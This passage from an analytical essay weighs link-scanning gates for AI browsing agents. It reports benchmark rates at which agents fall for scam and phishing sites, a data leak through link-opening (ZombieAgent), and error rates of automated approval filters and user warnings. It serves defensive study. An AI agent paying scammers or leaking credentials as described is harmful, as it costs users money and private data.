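| Qwen3.8 Flash | 18 | 30 | 27 | 8 | 0 | 100 |
| Kimi K3 | 23 | 32 | 36 | 10 | 20 | 100 |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 26 | 41 | 33 | 4 | 20 | 96 |
| DeepSeek V4.1 Flash | 35 | 58 | 49 | 8 | 60 | 100 |

The consent phishing sites requested more account access than the task required. There were only four of these sites, so the spread from 0% to 60% is weak evidence about any one model. Several of the models are also the smaller, faster ones in their families, and stronger models may do better.

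Agents went ahead in 28% of the scams that ended in a payment, but in only 2% of those that ended in a request for a password, card details or access to a crypto wallet.

Agents gave away passwords far more often in *CredLeakBench* than in *ScamWorld*, probably in part because the warning signs in *CredLeakBench* were mostly in the address, while those in *ScamWorld* were visible on the page. Wu and colleagues found that agents make little use of the address. Hiding it raised the share of successful scams by only 2 percentage points, and 3.2% of the agents' fraud warnings cited the address alone. A check that compares domains in code would therefore add evidence that agents mostly overlook.

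That evidence wouldn't help with every scam, because only 157 of the 363 sites posed as another business. The sites that fooled the most agents looked like ordinary shops asking for an ordinary payment. A plausible domain under the shop's own brand more than doubled the odds that the scam would succeed, and an ownership test wouldn't catch a shop like that.

A preflight check also has to improve on a much simpler measure, a warning in the user's request. Wu and colleagues added one sentence saying that some websites may be scams and telling the agent to check before paying or sharing details. Across three of the models, the share of scams that succeeded fell by 24 points, and on payment tasks it fell from 34% to 2%. With the warning, the agents completed 154 of 159 honest tasks, a rate about 3 points lower than without it. Telling the agents that their payments were real and irreversible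 made almost no difference.

Even this small loss could outweigh the gain if scams are rare. If one task in 1,000 led to a scam site, then for every 1,000 tasks the warning would prevent about 0.24 scams and stop about 30 legitimate tasks.

### Why most blocks would be wrong

When hostile links are rare, most of the links a check blocks can be harmless. Suppose that one link in 10,000 is hostile, and that the check catches 95% of hostile links and wrongly blocks 1% of harmless ones. Out of a million links, 100 are hostile and the check blocks 95 of them. It also blocks 9,999 harmless links, so fewer than 1% of its blocks are correct.

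The false blocks add up over a task. If an agent opens 30 pages and each harmless page has an independent 1% chance of a false block, the chance of at least one is 1 − 0.99³⁰, or about 26%. A lower false-block rate helps a lot:

| False-block rate | Share of blocks that are correct | 30-page tasks with a false block |
|---|---|---|
| 1% | 0.9% | 26% |
| 0.1% | 8.7% | 3.0% |
| 0.01% | 48.7% | 0.3% |

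Real errors aren't independent. A gate that wrongly blocks the hotel's payment company once will probably do so every time, so fewer tasks than estimated would encounter false blocks, but those that did would encounter them repeatedly. The rate of one in 10,000 is also only an assumption. Among links in emails from strangers, one in 100 might be hostile, in which case about half of the blocks would be correct even with a 1% false-block rate.

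Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports false-alarm rates for a similar filter in its programming agent, Claude Code. A fast first stage wrongly flagged 8.5% of 10,000 ordinary actions. The same model then reconsidered only the flagged actions, this time reasoning through each before deciding, which cut the rate to 0.4%. If those rates applied to each page visit in a 30-visit task, the first stage alone would wrongly flag at least one visit in 93% of tasks, and the two stages together would do so in about 11%.

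The second check raised the share of harmful actions that got through from 6.6% to 17%, though this is based on only 52 real cases in which the agent had gone further than the user wanted.

How much a false block disrupts a task depends on what happens next. In Claude Code, the agent receives the reason for the block and usually finds another way to proceed, so most false blocks lead to a single retry. Claude Code prompts the user only after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session.

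### How to scan less

An agent that follows CybrLab's *preclick* instructions would scan every link. At 75 seconds a scan, in the middle of the company's stated range, scanning 30 links one after another would take 37.5 minutes. The free allowance of 100 requests a day would cover three tasks of that size.

PreClick lets an agent shorten the wait by starting several scans at once. For example, the agent could submit the links to all ten hotels on a results page and have the answers in little more than a minute. But it would use up its scan allowance on links it never opens, and send those links to CybrLab.

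Scanning fewer pages saves more. The figures below continue the illustration, with 30 pages on six sites and a 1% false-block rate per scan:

| Pages that get a slow scan | Scans | Wait | Tasks with a false block | What goes unscanned |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Every page | 30 | 37.5 minutes | 26% | Nothing |
| The first page on each site, with the result cached | 6 | 7.5 minutes | 5.9% | A bad page on a good site, or a site that changes later |
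| Only pages that a quick first check can't clear, say three | 3 | 3.75 minutes | 3.0% | Anything the quick check wrongly clears |
| Only pages where the agent will log in or pay, say two | 2 | 2.5 minutes | 2.0% | Pages the agent only reads |

The third row assumes that the quick check blocks nothing by itself. A task with a download would add one scan to the last row.

Some results can be cached for longer than others. A domain's owner rarely changes, so a gate can keep that result for weeks, while a scan of the page's contents may be out of date within minutes. The gate can't reuse one private-data result for a whole site, because the agent may add private data, such as the surgery note, to the next address it opens there. But this test needs only the address and can be very fast.

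Whether a scan is worth the wait depends on the losses it prevents. Suppose waiting costs the user $10 an hour and a false block wastes one minute. Each 75-second scan then costs about 21 cents, or $2,100 for 10,000 links. Suppose also that one of those links is hostile, the agent would fall for it 20% of the time (close to the 22% average in ScamWorld), and the scan catches 95% of hostile links. The 10,000 scans would then prevent an average of 0.19 successful attacks, so they would be justified only if the average successful attack cost more than $11,000.

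A check that takes 30 milliseconds, with the same accuracy, would be worth using if the average loss were above about $92. A slow scan used only on links of which one in 100 is hostile would be worth using if the average loss were above about $110. These estimates are rough. The delay wastes less of the user's time when the agent works in the background, which favours scanning. But a convincing scam may fool both the agent and the scanner, so the scan would prevent fewer losses than this calculation assumes.

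### What people do with frequent warnings

Many gates pass doubtful links to the user, which helps only if the user reads the warning. People pay attention to warnings that are usually right. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) analysed more than 25 million browser warnings and found that users clicked through 9% to 23% of malware and phishing warnings, depending on the browser and the threat. These warnings were almost always accurate.

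Users clicked through 70% of Chrome's warnings about website certificates, which misconfigured but harmless sites often trigger. False alarms probably don't fully explain that rate, since Firefox users clicked through only 33% of the equivalent warnings. Firefox also saved users' exceptions, so it didn't show them the same warning again.

People heed repeated warnings less over time, even when they know the rules. *Tuning Out Security Warnings* (Vance et al., 2018) reports a field experiment in which 102 students installed apps on their own phones for three weeks. The students had passed a quiz on which permissions to refuse and received fewer than five warnings a day. Those whose warnings always looked the same refused 87% of the risky apps at the start and 55% at the end. Among students whose warnings kept changing in appearance, the rate fell only to 76%.

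Agents can ask for permission many times in a session. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts. In a test with 1,053 paid professionals, the company replaced one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic's automated check blocked 89% of the same commands, regardless of session length.

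Anthropic was making the case for its own product, and testers may care less about damage to projects that aren't their own. But that wouldn't easily explain why the testers got worse as the session went on.

OpenAI gives no data for its argument that frequent warnings train people to click through, but these studies support it.

Asking users less often doesn't guarantee better answers, though. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated agent. Seven of its 18 actions went beyond what the user had asked for. People who were asked about all 18 actions blocked 59.6% of the unwanted ones. When a model first picked out ten actions to ask about, including all seven unwanted ones, people blocked 53.9%. Removing eight prompts apparently reduced protection only a little,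 but people weren't more careful with the prompts that remained. Each session required only about two minutes of decisions, so the study couldn't measure fatigue over weeks.

Yan also let a third group set rules in advance. Participants in this group mostly chose "ask me", then approved two-thirds of the unwanted actions they were asked about. Overall, they blocked only about 40% of unwanted actions.

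A gate that learns from past approvals could make this worse. For *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115. They warn that repeated approval may reflect fatigue rather than a lasting preference. Five quick clicks on "allow" are therefore a poor reason to add a site to the user's trusted list.

The wording of the prompt matters too. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) reviews 290 incident reports about agents and files. In 80 of them, actions went ahead under automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt didn't tell the user what the action would do. A long web address is just as uninformative to the user, whereas a message like "This link goes to login-desk.example, which isn't your hotel's site" helps them decide.

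### What a scanning company learns

A hosted scanner receives the address of each page the agent wants to open. PreClick also requests the purpose of the visit, which the company would otherwise have to guess from the address. If an agent submits every link under one customer's key, the scanner's records could show which banks and doctors the user visits online, which jobs they apply for, and the reason for each visit. CybrLab's *PreClick MCP Server* page doesn't mention how long the company keeps this information.

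The address may also grant access to anyone who has it, like the password-reset links that Ramadan and colleagues found in public collections. They note that scanning services such as VirusTotal and URLScan.io often include submitted addresses in public reports. ClawHub advises users not to send PreClick any address that contains session tokens or login parameters. This advice is sensible, but it rules out many of the sign-in links that a worried user would most like to check.

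Developers can reduce what the scanner learns, usually by giving up some protection:

| Design | What an outside scanner learns | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Send the full address and the intent | The page, any code in its address, and the purpose | The most exposure |
| Send only the registrable domain | Which sites the agent visits | The scanner can't examine the exact page |
| Keep a copy of a blocklist on the device | Only addresses that match the list | The list misses new scams |
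| Compare domains on the device | Nothing | The device needs the real address first |

Chrome and Firefox used the third design when Akhawe and Felt studied them. Each browser regularly downloaded a list of suspicious sites and contacted Google about an address only if it matched the list. OpenAI runs its known-public-URL check itself and already handles the conversation, so the check doesn't reveal the agent's destination to an outside scanner.

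Privacy is harder to protect when the scanner needs to know the user's intent. A specific intent, such as "Confirm my room at hotel.example", helps the scanner judge whether a link fits the task, but it also reveals where the user is staying. Software on the device could first compare the link's domain with the hotel's name, then send the scanner only the general purpose of the task.

### Every link, or only the steps that matter?

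The argument for checking every link is that harm can happen before any step looks important, such as a leak through the address or an injection from the page. ZombieAgent leaked data just by opening links, without a login, payment or download to trigger a selective check. Software also can't always tell which steps matter, because opening an ordinary-looking link may cancel a booking. Automating the checks also avoids the fatigue a person would feel after reviewing many links.

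ScamWorld supports the case for checking only logins, payments, downloads and requests for account access, because payments caused most of the trouble there. In some of its scams, the decisive sign appears only at checkout, so a scan of the first page would miss it. Wu and colleagues recommend a check just before payment, when the recipient, fees and terms can be examined. None of these appear in a URL. Such a check is particularly useful because in 45% of the agents' failures, the agent had noted a specific risk and continued anyway, often reasoning that the user had asked for the purchase.

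Selective checks also produce fewer prompts, so people might read them. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans the agent presents for approval, compared with 3% of its requests to take a single action. The lower frequency of plans doesn't fully explain the difference, because a plan also gives people more to disagree with. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) describes screening by risk as the only approach said to combine low fatigue with high security, and found no product using it as of May. Anthropic's auto mode is similar in that it skips the check for low-risk actions.

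The two cases mostly concern different kinds of check, so a developer can accept both. The software can check every address with tests that take milliseconds on the device, such as comparing domains and looking for private data. Slow scans, outside services and questions to the user make more sense before consequential steps and for links from strangers. In the hotel task, the software would test all 30 addresses locally. It would run a scan only if the agent were about to follow a link from an unknown sender or type a card number into a site the user had never used.
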